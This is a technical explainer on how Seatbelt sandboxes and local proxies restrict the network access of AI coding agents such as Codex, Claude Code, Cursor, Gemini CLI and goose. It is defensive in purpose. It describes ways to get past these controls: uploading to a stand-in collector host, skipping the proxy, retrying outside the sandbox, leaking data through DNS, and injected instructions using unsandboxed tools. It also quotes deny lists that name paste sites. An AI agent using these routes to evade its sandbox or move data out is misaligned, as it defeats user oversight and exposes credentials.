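| Upload the notes | `localhost:3128` | `collector.example:443` | The proxy returns 403 with `blocked-by-allowlist` |
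| Skip the proxy | `203.0.113.7:443` | Nothing | The kernel refuses with "Operation not permitted" |

Seatbelt allows both the package request and the upload, because the kernel sees only two connections to port 3128 on the same Mac. The proxy checks the domain name in each request and refuses the upload before curl sends any of the file.

The proxy's allowlist has no effect on the command that skips the proxy. The profile allows no direct connection to any outside machine, so the command would fail even if 203.0.113.7 were the address of pypi.org. The example uses a numeric address to avoid a DNS lookup. With a hostname, curl would probably fail at the lookup, as in Gas Town's test.

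Zhao reports that connections to outside addresses fail immediately with "Operation not permitted", both from `curl --noproxy '*'` and from programs that open their own sockets. Like fG!'s much older telnet test, this is evidence that the kernel itself stops the connection.

### What each layer does

Seatbelt's port rule makes the local proxy a command's only route to the internet, and the proxy limits which domains the command can reach. Without the port rule, the proxy would filter only the programs that use it. Commands would have no internet access if the rule were applied without a proxy.

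If the user had enabled network access, Codex used to set the proxy variables but also put an unrestricted `(allow network-outbound)` in the profile, so a program that ignored the variables could bypass the proxy and connect to anything. The code change *feat(sandbox): enforce proxy-aware network routing in sandbox* replaced that rule with one for each proxy port in profiles used with a proxy. One of its tests checks that the unrestricted rule stays out of the profile even if the user has asked for full network access.

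If an administrator has set network requirements, the change also makes Codex apply the operating system's sandbox in a mode that normally runs commands without one. Otherwise, nothing would force commands to use the proxy. However, if the sandbox blocks a command and the user approves a retry, the same code allows Codex to run the retry without the sandbox. A program can then bypass the proxy by ignoring the proxy variables.

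Zhao ran 80 attacks in eight categories against a system that combines a kernel sandbox, a proxy and other defences. All of the attacks succeeded in an unprotected environment, and none succeeded against the full system. When Zhao switched off a component, the attacks it was meant to stop succeeded again, which supports the view that the components stop different attacks. The results are weaker evidence that the system would stop a new attack, since Zhao designed both the defences and the tests.

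Keeping the domain allowlist in the proxy also allows users to change the network policy without rewriting the profile. The Seatbelt rule specifies a port but no domains, so any proxy can listen on that port. Anthropic lets users substitute their own proxy to enforce rules that the standard one does not support.

### Why the proxy runs outside the sandbox

A proxy running under the same Seatbelt profile as the commands could connect to its own port but not to pypi.org, so it could not forward their requests. Relaxing the profile to allow the proxy's outside connections would also allow the commands to make them directly, because Seatbelt applies a profile's rules to every process running under it.

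Commands must not be able to change the proxy's program or its domain list, or they could approve their own destinations. Running the proxy as a separate process outside the sandbox isn't enough, because its settings also need protection. Codex keeps network settings in `config.toml`, and its file rules protect the domain list by making an existing `.codex` directory in the workspace, including everything inside it, read-only for commands.

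Several agents on one Mac may need different permissions. Zhao gives each sandbox its own proxy port and identifies the agent by that port rather than by a name in a request header, which a hostile command could forge. Each profile opens only one port, so an agent cannot use another agent's permissions by connecting to that agent's proxy port.

### What happens if the settings are wrong?

The profile and the environment variables have to use the same port. If the variables point to port 3128 and the profile allows only 3129, ordinary commands will fail. It would be worse to treat a broken proxy setting as if the user had not asked for a proxy, and allow unrestricted network access.

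Codex avoids disagreement by building the Seatbelt rules from the same variables that it gives to commands. For each proxy variable, it reads the value as a URL and skips it if it is empty or malformed, or if the host is anything other than `localhost`, 127.0.0.1 or ::1. It then takes the port from the URL, or uses the usual port for that type of proxy if the URL has none. Two valid settings with ports 43128 and 48081 produce these rules:

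```
(allow network-outbound (remote ip "localhost:43128"))
(allow network-outbound (remote ip "localhost:48081"))
```

What goes into the profile depends on whether Codex finds a usable port:

| Situation | Network access in the profile |
|---|---|
| At least one valid loopback proxy | The proxy ports, plus other local traffic if the user has enabled it |
| Proxy settings exist, but none is valid | None |
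| An administrator requires a managed network, but there is no usable proxy | None |
| No proxy and no such requirement, with full network access on | All outbound and inbound traffic |
| No proxy and no such requirement, with full network access off | None |

*feat(sandbox): enforce proxy-aware network routing in sandbox* describes its treatment of unusable settings as failing closed, which means blocking traffic when a component is missing or misconfigured. The tests cover both cases with network access switched on, where a mistake would do the most harm. If only one of several settings is malformed, Codex keeps the valid ports. Programs that use the malformed setting lose their connection and still cannot connect directly.

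*zerobox-sandboxing* achieves a similar result more simply. It uses restricted rules if it finds a valid port, any proxy setting (even an invalid one), or a requirement for a managed network. A broken proxy setting therefore adds no port rule and no general permission to connect, though other services on the same Mac may still be reachable if the user has enabled that access.

The port rule also gives some protection if the proxy crashes. The profile still blocks direct connections, and attempts to reach the proxy fail because nothing is listening on its port. But if another program on the Mac starts listening there, sandboxed commands can connect to it, because the rule specifies only the port, not which program is using it.

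A bug in Anthropic's sandbox runtime, the open-source software behind Claude Code's sandbox, could let commands make outside requests if the policy contained no allowed domains, according to GitLab's security advisory *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing*. As with Microsoft's MXC, a user could choose a restrictive policy and get an open network. Anthropic fixed the bug in version 0.0.16. An empty allowlist should be the strictest setting, and Codex's proxy treats it that way by blocking every request until the user adds a permission.

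### A localhost port or a Unix socket?

Anthropic's October 2025 post describes Claude Code as reaching the network through "a unix domain socket connected to a proxy server running outside the sandbox". That does not match the port rule on macOS. *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime*, a guide to the software, says the HTTP and SOCKS5 proxies use localhost ports on macOS and Unix sockets on Linux. The post evidently describes the Linux design as if it applied to both systems.

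The difference comes from how each system isolates a command. On Linux, the sandbox can put the command in a network namespace, which has its own network interfaces, including loopback. A command that connects to 127.0.0.1:3128 inside the namespace therefore cannot reach a proxy on the host. But the sandbox can make a Unix socket's file available to both the command and the host.

macOS has no equivalent of a network namespace. A command under Seatbelt uses the same loopback as every other program on the Mac, and it can reach the proxy's port directly if the profile permits it. A profile could allow a particular Unix socket instead, but ordinary proxy settings contain a host and port, and many programs cannot use a socket path in their place.

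Linux sandboxes face the same limitation. For containers without a network, Anthropic suggests running the proxy on the host, mounting its Unix socket in the container, and relaying a localhost port inside the container to that socket, so that curl can use a normal proxy address. Zhao's Linux version has a similar relay, and adds a random token for each sandbox because other agents' socket files may be visible inside the sandbox. Without the token, one agent could connect to another's socket and use its permissions.

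## What do the shipped agents allow by default?

Codex blocks network access for the agent's commands until the user turns it on, and Cursor blocks it for commands in its sandbox. Three other agents that use Seatbelt filter network traffic only after the user changes a setting. Claude Code and the open-source agent goose ship with their sandboxes off, and Gemini CLI's standard Seatbelt profile allows all outbound traffic.

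### The order of releases

Google's version came first, in 2025, when the Gemini CLI code change *restricted networking for all sandboxing methods, new seatbelt profiles, updated docs* added profiles that allow outbound connections only to port 8877 on the same Mac. Users had to supply the proxy themselves. Anthropic released Claude Code's sandbox in October 2025, which includes a proxy and prompts the user about new domains.

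Cursor at first gave sandboxed commands no network access, according to *Agent Sandboxing*, its announcement for version 2.0. It added domain rules in version 2.5. By February 2026, goose had a macOS sandbox with a filtering proxy. Codex had its managed proxy by April 2026, when OpenAI shortened the list of destinations that programs contact directly instead of through the proxy.

### The defaults compared

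The table follows the makers' documentation and, for Gemini CLI, the 2025 code change. The dates matter because these settings change often. In June 2026, for example, Anthropic described Claude Code's sandbox as covering only Bash commands, but by October it also covered commands from the PowerShell and Monitor tools.

| Agent | Network by default | Domain list | At an unknown domain | What the sandbox covers | What an administrator can lock | Date of entry |
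|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Open until the user turns on the sandbox | Allowlist, on with the sandbox, initially empty | Usually asks the user | Bash, PowerShell and Monitor commands | Sandbox use, allowed domains, retries outside the sandbox | 21 October 2026 |
| Codex | Off | Allowlist, initially empty; its proxy is off | Refuses or seeks approval | Local commands | Sandbox modes, network rules, permission profiles | 26 May and 2 July 2026 |
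| Cursor | Off for sandboxed commands | Allowlist, initially empty; a built-in list is available | Refuses | Terminal commands | Allowed and denied domains | August and 28 November 2026 |
| Gemini CLI | Open | None built in | Depends on the user's proxy | The whole program | No lock in this code change | 2025 |
| goose Desktop | Open until the user turns on the sandbox | Blocklist, on with the sandbox | Connects | The whole backend | Domain rules, through an outside service | 7 April 2026 |

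### Claude Code

A user turns on the sandbox with the `/sandbox` command. The list of allowed domains starts empty, so the first command that contacts pypi.org normally leads to a prompt. Answering "Yes" allows the domain for the rest of the session. "Yes, and don't ask again" saves a rule that also allows it in later sessions.

The saved rule is a permission for WebFetch, the tool Claude uses to read web pages, but Anthropic also applies these permissions to sandboxed commands. A user who permanently lets Claude read a site has therefore let those commands upload files to it. The sandbox's domain list does not limit WebFetch, which runs outside the sandbox and follows separate permission rules. Claude's file tools also run outside the sandbox, as do hooks (commands that Claude Code runs automatically at set moments) and local MCP servers (programs that give the agent extra tools). If the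 proxy stops an injected instruction from sending data with curl, the agent may still be able to send it through one of these.

Access to unlisted domains depends on the permission mode. In `bypassPermissions` mode, which skips most permission prompts, commands can reach any host the user has not explicitly denied. This mode therefore removes most of the network limit, though a developer might choose it because the sandbox seems to make prompts unnecessary.

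In auto mode, a classifier (a separate model that reviews the agent's actions) takes the user's place. Claude lists the hosts a command needs, and the classifier reviews the list together with the command. If the classifier approves, Claude Code opens those hosts for that command only. If the command tries another host, Claude Code refuses the connection, and Claude can rerun the command with a longer list.

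A user who wants a fixed list can set `strictAllowlist`, available since version 2.1.219. The proxy then refuses unlisted hosts in every mode.

When Claude Code's sandbox blocks a host, the command's result includes the host, and Claude may ask to rerun the command outside the sandbox. In the ordinary manual mode, the user sees a prompt to approve the retry. But a saved permission such as `Bash(curl *)` also approves it, and curl then runs with no domain list. Setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to `false` turns off these retries.

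Anthropic's sandbox-runtime also works without Claude Code. *Sandboxing*, an earlier edition of Anthropic's documentation, gives the example of confining an MCP server with it. A user can also run all of Claude Code inside it, which puts WebFetch, hooks and local MCP servers under the same network limits as shell commands.

### Codex

In Codex, `network_access` determines whether commands have a network connection, and `network_proxy` determines whether the proxy filters it. Both are off by default. OpenAI documents what happens when a user turns on one or both:

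| `network_access` | `network_proxy` | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Off | On | No network access; the proxy setting does nothing |
| On | Off | Unrestricted direct access |
| On | On | Access limited by the proxy's rules |

The risky combination is also the easiest to reach. A user whose package installation fails can fix it by setting `network_access = true`, which gives every command unrestricted network access. If the user then turns on the proxy without adding any domains, commands can't reach any outside host.

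When a request is blocked, Codex can ask for approval. It asks the user by default, but with `approvals_reviewer = "auto_review"`, eligible approval requests go to a reviewer agent instead. The agent checks whether the action might steal data or search for credentials, among other things, and can approve low-risk and medium-risk actions without involving the user. If the user has set Codex never to ask, neither the user nor the agent can approve a blocked request.

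OpenAI's *Permissions* describes a newer system, still in beta in July 2026, in which one named profile holds both file and network rules. Network access is again off by default. If a profile's only network setting is `enabled = true`, Codex gives commands full network access. Yet according to the document's settings table, Codex blocks domain requests if a profile has no allow entries. The likely explanation is that Codex applies domain rules only if the profile contains some, so it is safest to add them in the same edit that enables the network.

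If `sandbox_mode` appears in any configuration file that Codex loads, Codex uses the older sandbox settings and ignores the user's chosen profile, unless an administrator has required profiles. An old `sandbox_mode` line in one file can therefore disable a list of domains that a developer wrote in another.

On macOS, Codex refuses to run a command if Seatbelt cannot enforce the selected policy. Claude Code is less strict and by default runs commands without a sandbox if the sandbox cannot start. Seatbelt comes with every Mac, so Claude Code's default is mostly a risk on Linux, where users have to install the required packages.

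The domain rules cover local commands. MCP servers, connectors to other services and browser control have their own settings, and web search is also separate. By default, Codex searches OpenAI's index of web pages instead of fetching live ones. This makes it harder for an attacker to get the agent to read a new page, although the indexed pages can still contain prompt injections.

### Gemini CLI, goose and Cursor

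Gemini CLI's proxied profiles work only with a proxy that the user provides. The user sets `GEMINI_SANDBOX_PROXY_COMMAND` to a command that starts one, and Gemini CLI waits until some program is listening on port 8877. The sample proxy permits only example.com on port 443, so the user has to extend it before doing real work. Because all of Gemini CLI runs in the sandbox, the proxy also has to permit the agent's connections to its language model.

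In Gemini CLI, the profile and the proxy command are separate settings. If a user chooses a proxied profile but sets no proxy command, commands usually have no network access because nothing is listening on the port. Setting the proxy command but keeping the default profile is a worse mistake, because Gemini CLI starts the proxy and sets the proxy variables, but Seatbelt still allows direct connections. Codex once had the same gap.

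The instructions also tell users to make the proxy listen on 0.0.0.0, meaning every network address the Mac has, whereas Codex's proxy listens only on loopback by default.

goose uses a blocklist instead of an allowlist. If the user launches the desktop app with `GOOSE_SANDBOX=true`, it starts a proxy and runs its backend, `goosed`, under Seatbelt. The proxy refuses the domains in a file called `blocked.txt` and permits most others. goose's documentation describes this as blocking "unapproved domains", but an unlisted domain needs no approval.

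goose's example blocklist includes pastebin.com and webhook.site, which are convenient places to send stolen text. An attacker can avoid the list by registering a new domain. goose also has some narrower rules, such as limiting SSH to known Git hosting sites, but its domain filter protects much less than an allowlist would.

Cursor also uses Seatbelt on macOS. It considered App Sandbox, containers and virtual machines, and found that App Sandbox would have required Cursor to sign every program an agent might run. Seatbelt cannot apply domain rules, so Cursor presumably uses a local proxy for them, although its settings reference does not describe one.

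According to Cursor's *sandbox.json reference*, Cursor denies network access by default, and its list of allowed domains is empty. Users can choose between their own list, their list plus Cursor's built-in domains, and full network access. Unlike in Codex, the pattern `*.example.com` also matches example.com itself.

A command may still need approval even if the domain it contacts is on the list. In the forum post *Auto-Run network access `sandbox.json + Defaults` seems to not be working*, a user reported that Cursor's agent would not run `curl apache.org` automatically, even though apache.org was among the built-in domains. The agent did run it when the user allowed all network access.

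### How OpenAI configures Codex for its own staff

In *Running Codex safely at OpenAI*, published on 8 May, OpenAI (2026) gave parts of its internal configuration. The network settings are short:

```
[experimental_network]
enabled = true
allow_local_binding = true
denied_domains = ["pastebin.com"]
allowed_domains = ["login.microsoftonline.com", "*.openai.com"]
```

Commands run by Codex can reach Microsoft's sign-in service and OpenAI's own subdomains without approval. Unlisted domains require approval from the user or a reviewer agent. Commands can never reach pastebin.com through the proxy, because it is explicitly denied and neither the user nor the reviewer agent can override a denial.

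OpenAI's published list has no package registry, which is surprising for a company with many programmers. OpenAI may have shortened the list for the post, or may rely on approvals for registries. It uses automatic review internally, so some requests for new domains may be approved without a person seeing them.

OpenAI also restricts staff to the read-only and workspace-write sandbox modes, so they can't run Codex without a sandbox, and limits web search to its own index. In other respects, its staff settings are more permissive than Codex's defaults. `allow_local_binding` gives commands wider access to services on the same Mac, and separate rules let a few common commands run outside the sandbox without approval.

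OpenAI logs the proxy's decisions and uses them to measure how often the sandbox blocks requests or asks for approval. If security software on a computer raises an alert about Codex, an AI agent examines the logs, including the user's original request, and sends its analysis to the security team. The post gives no figures for blocked requests or prevented attacks, so it is useful as an example configuration but not as evidence of how well the configuration works.

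### What administrators can lock

An organisation may want settings that neither a developer nor a downloaded project can loosen. For Claude Code, Anthropic recommends starting with three managed settings, which the administrator distributes to every machine:

```
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
  }
}
```

These settings turn on the sandbox, stop Claude Code from starting without it, and keep Claude from retrying blocked commands outside it. A managed on-or-off setting overrides the developer's, but Claude Code combines lists from several settings files, so a developer can still add domains to the administrator's list.

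`allowManagedDomainsOnly` closes that gap by making Claude Code use only the administrator's allowed domains and refuse all others without a prompt. The setting also stops developers from replacing the proxy. A replacement proxy does its own filtering, so Anthropic's domain lists no longer apply to traffic sent through it. Before version 2.1.285, any settings file, including one in a downloaded repository, could set the proxy's port. To exploit this, an attacker would also have needed a suitable proxy already listening on the Mac.

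Codex administrators set rules in `requirements.toml`, which users cannot override. Administrators can use it to start the proxy even if the user has not enabled it, but this does not give commands network access that the sandbox denies. They can also list the permission profiles that users may choose. Codex denies every profile missing from that list, including any built-in ones that OpenAI adds in future versions.

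In Cursor, an administrator's allowlist replaces the user's and the project's, but denied domains from all sources still apply. Without an administrator's allowlist, Cursor combines the user's allowed domains with those in the project's `.cursor/sandbox.json`. A project downloaded from a stranger can therefore allow extra domains that a user would miss by checking only their personal settings.

goose can take its domain rules from LaunchDarkly, a service through which companies change software settings remotely. The administrator has to decide what happens if LaunchDarkly is unreachable, and the choices are to allow traffic, deny it or use the local blocklist. Only `deny` fails closed. The developer still has to turn on the sandbox through an environment variable, so these rules have no effect on someone who launches goose normally.

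### When an empty list meant no limit

In version 0.0.16, Anthropic fixed a sandbox-runtime bug that could leave the network open if the policy allowed no domains. That configuration was common, because an allowlist is empty until someone adds a domain. GitLab's *CVE-2025-66479* (4 December 2025) is the public advisory.

The title of the post *allowedDomains*, by a researcher who found the bug independently, quotes the software's documentation: "Empty array = no network access." The researcher says that another user raised the problem on GitHub on 18 November 2025, and that he himself reported it to Anthropic three days later and demonstrated that it affected Claude Code. Anthropic fixed the library on 24 November and Claude Code on 26 November. Claude Code's release notes described a correction to the proxy's DNS behaviour and did not mention a security problem, and the public advisory covered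 only the library.

*CVE-2025-66479* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, gives the bug a severity score of 1.8 out of 10, which the researcher considers too low. The score may be low partly because an attacker would still have needed to get hostile code or instructions into the sandbox. But a sandbox for coding agents is meant for that situation, and a user who relied on the empty list to keep credentials on the machine could have had no protection.

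A program can easily make this kind of mistake if it only checks whether the list contains any domains, because it then treats an empty list like a missing one. A missing list may mean that the user has not asked for filtering, whereas an empty list is a request to block everything. It is unclear from GitLab's advisory whether this was the error in sandbox-runtime.

An empty allowlist must block every domain, as it does in Cursor and in Codex's proxy. Codex's proxy also blocks outside domains if the list is missing. Codex's permission profiles are less safe here, because enabling the network without adding domain rules opens it completely. Developers can test this by running `curl https://example.com` under an empty list and checking that it fails.

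## Who resolves names for a sandboxed command?

When a command uses the local proxy, the proxy normally resolves names for it. A command can also try to resolve a name itself, either through mDNSResponder or by querying a DNS server directly. The proxy's domain allowlist covers neither route, so only the sandbox profile can block them. Blocking them breaks some ordinary tools, and developers disagree about how strict the profile should be.

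### How macOS resolves a name

Most programs call `getaddrinfo`, a library function that turns a name into addresses. *Some things about getaddrinfo that surprised me* (Evans, 2022) uses this function to explain why two programs on one machine can resolve the same name differently. For example, a Python program checks the hosts file first, but `dig`, a command-line tool for querying DNS, does not.

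On a Mac, a lookup through `getaddrinfo` takes these steps, according to Apple's source code for an older version of the library:

1. The program passes a name to `getaddrinfo`.
2. If the name has no dot, the library normally adds the Mac's search domains, so `wiki` might become `wiki.corp.example`.
3. The library passes the full name to mDNSResponder.
4. mDNSResponder answers from its cache or queries a DNS server.
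5. The library returns the addresses to the program.

mDNSResponder is a separate process that starts when the Mac boots. Its name refers to multicast DNS, which devices on a local network use to find each other without a DNS server. The manual page *mDNSResponder* describes it as the system-wide resolver for ordinary DNS too. Programs reach it through a Unix socket at `/private/var/run/mDNSResponder`.

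The agent's profile does not apply to mDNSResponder, because the command did not start it. A command that cannot open outside connections can still cause a DNS query to leave the Mac if it can reach mDNSResponder's socket. This is probably what happened in fG!'s telnet test, where the lookup of www.google.com succeeded and Seatbelt then refused the connection.

According to its macOS manual page, BIND 9's `dig` bypasses the system's name resolution. It reads DNS server addresses from `/etc/resolv.conf`, or takes one from the command line, and sends its own packets there, normally to port 53. Its answers may differ from those other programs get, so even outside a sandbox, a successful `dig` doesn't prove that curl can resolve the same name.

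### Which rules open each route?

A profile for the package manager Nix opens both routes. Dolstra wrote it for builds that need to download files, and Lix, a fork of Nix, includes it too. Its main network rules are:

```
(allow network* (local ip) (remote ip))
(allow network-outbound
    (remote unix-socket
        (path-literal "/private/var/run/mDNSResponder")))
```

The first rule allows all IP traffic, including DNS queries to port 53 on any machine. The second lets a program send name lookups to mDNSResponder. Other rules in the profile let programs read `/etc/resolv.conf`, where `dig` finds its DNS servers.

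Nix can leave the network this open because it uses this profile for downloads whose expected hash (a short fingerprint of the contents) the package author has stated in advance. If a file has changed, the hash doesn't match and the build fails. That protects the user from bad downloads, but it doesn't stop a program from sending data out, which is the main worry with a coding agent.

WebKit's sandbox profile allows access to the same socket. The profile also has a rule for outbound UDP, but Apple put it among the settings for Kerberos, a sign-in system, with a note to remove it once certain bugs are fixed. WebKit's ordinary name lookups therefore evidently need only the socket.

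The socket may not be the only way to reach mDNSResponder. Apple's source for the service has an optional component for XPC, which passes messages between processes. XPC relies on Mach services, which a Seatbelt profile controls with `mach-lookup` rules instead of network rules. The code editor Zed's sandbox used to allow unrestricted access to Mach services. Feldman's *Tighten macOS Seatbelt sandbox permissions* replaced that access with a list that includes the services needed for DNS.

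A profile such as Zhao's, which allows everything by default and then denies `network-outbound`, blocks access to the socket but might leave an XPC route open. Developers who want to block every lookup should test with both curl and programs that use Apple's newer networking interfaces.

| Profile | mDNSResponder's socket | Port 53 on other machines |
|---|---|---|
| WebKit | Open | Open, along with all other TCP and UDP |
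| Nix and Lix, for downloads | Open | Open, along with all other IP traffic |
| goose | Open | Closed |
| Zhao's port rule | Closed | Closed |

### Leaving the lookup to the proxy

With HTTP CONNECT, a command needs neither route, because it leaves the lookup to the proxy.

With a SOCKS proxy, the outcome depends on the first part of the proxy's address. Everything curl distinguishes four forms:

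| Proxy setting | Who resolves the name |
|---|---|
| `socks4://` | curl |
| `socks4a://` | The proxy |
| `socks5://` | curl |
| `socks5h://` | The proxy |

The protocol is the same for `socks5` and `socks5h`. The extra letter only tells curl to send the name instead of an address.

curl's command-line options for this are easy to misread. On curl's mailing list, a user asked how to stop curl from resolving names locally with `--socks5`. Stenberg (2019), in *Why resolve the dns locally when using a socks5 proxy*, told him to use `--socks5-hostname`. The user had already seen that option but thought it set the host name of the proxy server.

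Suppose a developer writes `socks5://127.0.0.1:8081` in the proxy settings of a strict sandbox. curl calls `getaddrinfo` to look up pypi.org, and `getaddrinfo` tries to reach mDNSResponder. Seatbelt blocks the attempt, so the lookup fails and curl exits without contacting the proxy. The proxy's log has no record of the request, so a developer who looks only there may conclude that curl ignored the proxy settings.

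Changing `socks5` to `socks5h` fixes the problem without opening DNS, because curl then sends the hostname to the proxy. This is presumably why OpenAI uses `socks5h` in its instructions for Codex's proxy. If the sandbox allowed DNS instead, curl would look up pypi.org itself and send the proxy only an IP address, which the proxy could not compare with the domain allowlist. A proxy that requires an approved domain would refuse the request.

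### What breaks when DNS is closed?

The most obvious drawback of a strict profile is that DNS diagnostic tools such as `dig` stop working. If a developer asks an agent why a new domain doesn't work, the agent may run `dig`, which fails whatever the state of the domain, and then report a DNS fault that doesn't exist. The user can avoid this by approving a single `dig` command outside the sandbox, if the agent permits that.

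Many companies have internal names that only their own DNS servers can resolve. A proxy that uses the Mac's normal resolver can look them up, but short names may still fail the allowlist check. `getaddrinfo` might expand `wiki` to `wiki.corp.example`, but a program that leaves the lookup to the proxy may send just `wiki`, which does not match an entry for the full name. The proxy may also refuse an internal name because it resolves to a private address.

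Some programs look up a host before connecting, to check that it exists or to choose between IPv4 and IPv6. If the lookup fails, they stop, even if they would have connected through the proxy. Allowing DNS lookups can be enough to make these programs work.

A working DNS lookup would not be enough for a program that connects directly. In the bug report *Sandboxed DNS resolution intermittently fails for external Postgres endpoints*, a Codex user on macOS describes a tool that uses a remote Postgres database. The tool sometimes failed with "no such host" inside the default sandbox, but the same command worked as soon as the user ran it with wider permissions. If the tool was connecting directly, it would have failed in the sandbox even with a working lookup, because Seatbelt would have blocked the database connection.

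The report does not establish the cause. A profile that always blocks lookups should produce the same error every time, but some commands succeeded and later ones failed. The agent was writing to a shared database, and because the error was unclear, it had to check after each failure whether an earlier write had partly succeeded before trying again, or risk creating a duplicate. The user asked for consistent behaviour or an error that named the network restriction.

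### What an open DNS route gives up

A DNS lookup can carry data out of the Mac, and one that bypasses the proxy also bypasses the domain allowlist. Allowing direct DNS lookups therefore weakens the protection against data theft, even if every other connection goes through the proxy.

goose accepts this risk. goose always allows access to mDNSResponder when its sandbox is on, and users cannot turn that off. A domain in `blocked.txt` is off limits for connections through the proxy, but a command can still look it up. This keeps ordinary programs working, and the loss is smaller than it would be with an allowlist, since goose's blocklist already lets commands connect to most domains.

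httpjail, a tool that filters the web requests of a single program, also began with DNS open. At its launch, as Willison (2025), in *httpjail*, reported, it allowed all DNS traffic on UDP port 53 and blocked everything else that was not HTTP or HTTPS. The project's later documentation, *httpjail*, lists protection against data leaking through DNS queries among its features. Its developers evidently came to see the open port as a weakness.

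If a developer has to open one route, the mDNSResponder socket is the narrower choice. The profile can specify that exact socket, and mDNSResponder sends queries to the servers configured for the Mac, where a company may already filter or log them. A rule for port 53 has to allow traffic to port 53 on any machine, so a command can choose its own DNS server. But `dig` doesn't use mDNSResponder, so opening the socket would not make it work.

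### How Codex came to allow port 53

In March 2026, Codex still kept port 53 closed for commands that used its managed proxy. *Improve macOS Seatbelt network and unix socket handling* (viyatb-oai, 2026) made it easier for these commands to run local servers but still limited their traffic to loopback and the proxy.

On 10 April, the same developer changed this to fix a problem with private DNS in a managed configuration, which is one that an administrator controls. The change's description in OpenAI's *Codex CLI*, the project's code repository, gives two causes besides the domain suffixes in `NO_PROXY`:

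- Tools such as `dig` ignore `HTTP_PROXY` and `ALL_PROXY`. They sent their queries directly, and Seatbelt blocked them.
- The administrator had set `allow_local_binding = true`, but this only let commands claim ports on `localhost`. `dig` may claim a port on all of the Mac's addresses, which it needs in order to talk to an outside server.

Besides removing the suffixes, OpenAI changed what `allow_local_binding` does on macOS. If the setting is on, commands can claim ports on any local address and send traffic to port 53 on other machines. In a Seatbelt profile, such permissions look like this:

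```
(allow network-bind (local ip "*:*"))
(allow network-outbound (remote ip "*:53"))
```

This is much narrower than unrestricted network access, and it keeps port 53 closed unless local binding is enabled. An administrator who has enabled it has already accepted some extra risk. The setting also affects internal names, because Codex's proxy normally refuses names that resolve to private addresses unless local binding is on.

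But the same setting now controls both local binding and DNS. A developer who wants an agent to run a test server on port 8080 doesn't need `dig`, but turning on local binding also lets every command query any DNS server on the internet. A separate DNS setting would have avoided this. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes `allow_local_binding` only as giving wider access to local and private destinations, so a user who relies on that description has no reason to expect the setting to allow access to public servers.

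The setting is off by default, but it was on in the sample configuration in an older OpenAI document, *network proxy*, and in the configuration OpenAI published for its own staff in May. On a Mac with the April change, the staff configuration would let commands send DNS queries for any domain, although the proxy would block their connections to pastebin.com.

There is no public sign that OpenAI has since revised the port 53 rule. In June, OpenAI still described local binding in the same terms. Navigara's *viyatb-oai* (2026), a page of statistics about the developer's work, lists the ten largest of 50 code changes from July to September, and none of the ten concerns the rule. The list is weak evidence, because a revision could have been too small to make the list or could have come from someone else.

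Users can test their own version with a command that Codex provides for trying out its sandbox:

```
codex sandbox macos --log-denials dig pypi.org
```

The test is most useful when run twice with the managed proxy running, first with local binding off and then with it on. If `dig` returns an answer, port 53 is open. If it fails, the denial log should help distinguish a Seatbelt block from an ordinary DNS fault.

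### Resolvers that limit what a command can look up

The simplest fix is to resolve names only at the proxy and leave both DNS routes closed. Tools that need direct lookups will then fail.

A sandbox could also run its own DNS resolver next to the proxy and answer queries only for approved names. Greyhaven's *Greywall*, a sandbox for command-line agents, has part of this design. By default, it uses a SOCKS5 proxy on localhost port 43052 and sends DNS queries to port 43053. On Linux, it can capture a command's DNS traffic and redirect it. This is harder on macOS because there are no network namespaces and `getaddrinfo` sends queries to mDNSResponder instead of a server the sandbox chooses. `dig` could still use a local resolver, since it accepts a server and port on the command line.

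A filtering resolver refuses to answer for names that its operator considers harmful. Ziplock, a program that runs Claude Code under Seatbelt, uses one instead of a domain allowlist. In *Ziplock*, thejefflarson explains that the Seatbelt profile limits IP connections to localhost, and a local proxy resolves each name through a Cloudflare service that blocks known malware and adult sites. The proxy sends its queries over HTTPS, which makes it harder for others on the network to read or change them. It also refuses requests for numeric public addresses, because these need no lookup and would bypass the filter.

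Ziplock's filter requires no setup and covers far more harmful domains than a user could list by hand. But thejefflarson acknowledges that it does not stop an agent from sending data to legitimate sites such as github.com and pastebin.com, or to a newly registered domain that Cloudflare has not yet categorised. Lookups of internal company names are also likely to fail, since a public resolver has no records for them.

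Ziplock also allows access to most Unix sockets. If that includes the mDNSResponder socket, a command can avoid Cloudflare's filter by looking up names through the Mac's ordinary resolver. It would still need the proxy to connect to the site.

A filtering resolver is therefore more useful as an addition to a domain allowlist than as a replacement. It adds little to a list that contains only pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org, but with a broad rule such as `*`, it could block some malicious domains that the proxy would allow.

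Companies can also control DNS outside the Mac. OpenAI recommends that users worried about hostile DNS answers add another layer of network control, such as a firewall or a company proxy. A firewall can allow DNS queries only to the company's own servers, which Seatbelt's port 53 rule cannot do. `dig` would then work for internal names, and the company could filter and log every query sent to port 53.

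## What happens to programs that ignore the proxy settings?

A program that ignores the proxy settings usually can't connect at all, because the sandbox profile blocks direct connections. This prevents data from leaving the Mac over those connections, but it also prevents useful tools from reaching even approved domains. It becomes a security problem when users run a broken tool outside the sandbox to get it working.

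### How programs read the proxy variables

`HTTP_PROXY`, `HTTPS_PROXY`, `ALL_PROXY` and `NO_PROXY` are a convention that no standard defines and macOS does not enforce. Each program, or the networking library it uses, has to read the variables and apply them.

Programs that follow the convention still differ in which variables they read and how they interpret them. curl reads `http_proxy` only in lower case, because some web servers copy a request's `Proxy` header into `HTTP_PROXY`, which would let whoever sent the request choose curl's proxy. wget reads the HTTP and HTTPS variables but not `ALL_PROXY`. Current versions of curl accept an address range such as 10.0.0.0/8 in `NO_PROXY`, while some other clients only compare text.

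Agents therefore set more than four variables. In Codex, *feat(sandbox): enforce proxy-aware network routing in sandbox* added families of the standard names and variants for particular tools. For example, pip, Python's package installer, has `PIP_PROXY`, and npm, the JavaScript package manager, has `npm_config_https_proxy`. Extra variables help only if a tool has one and the agent's developers know about it.

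### Which programs work?

Anthropic lists curl, npm and git over HTTPS among the tools that work in Claude Code's sandbox once the user has allowed the host. Git uses curl's library for HTTPS, so it reads the same proxy variables as curl, but its own `http.proxy` setting overrides them. If a developer has set `http.proxy` to a company proxy, git will try to connect to that proxy from inside the sandbox, and Seatbelt will block it. To use a company proxy with Claude Code, the user puts its address in `HTTPS_PROXY` before starting Claude Code, which then checks each domain against the allowlist and forwards approved connections to the company proxy.

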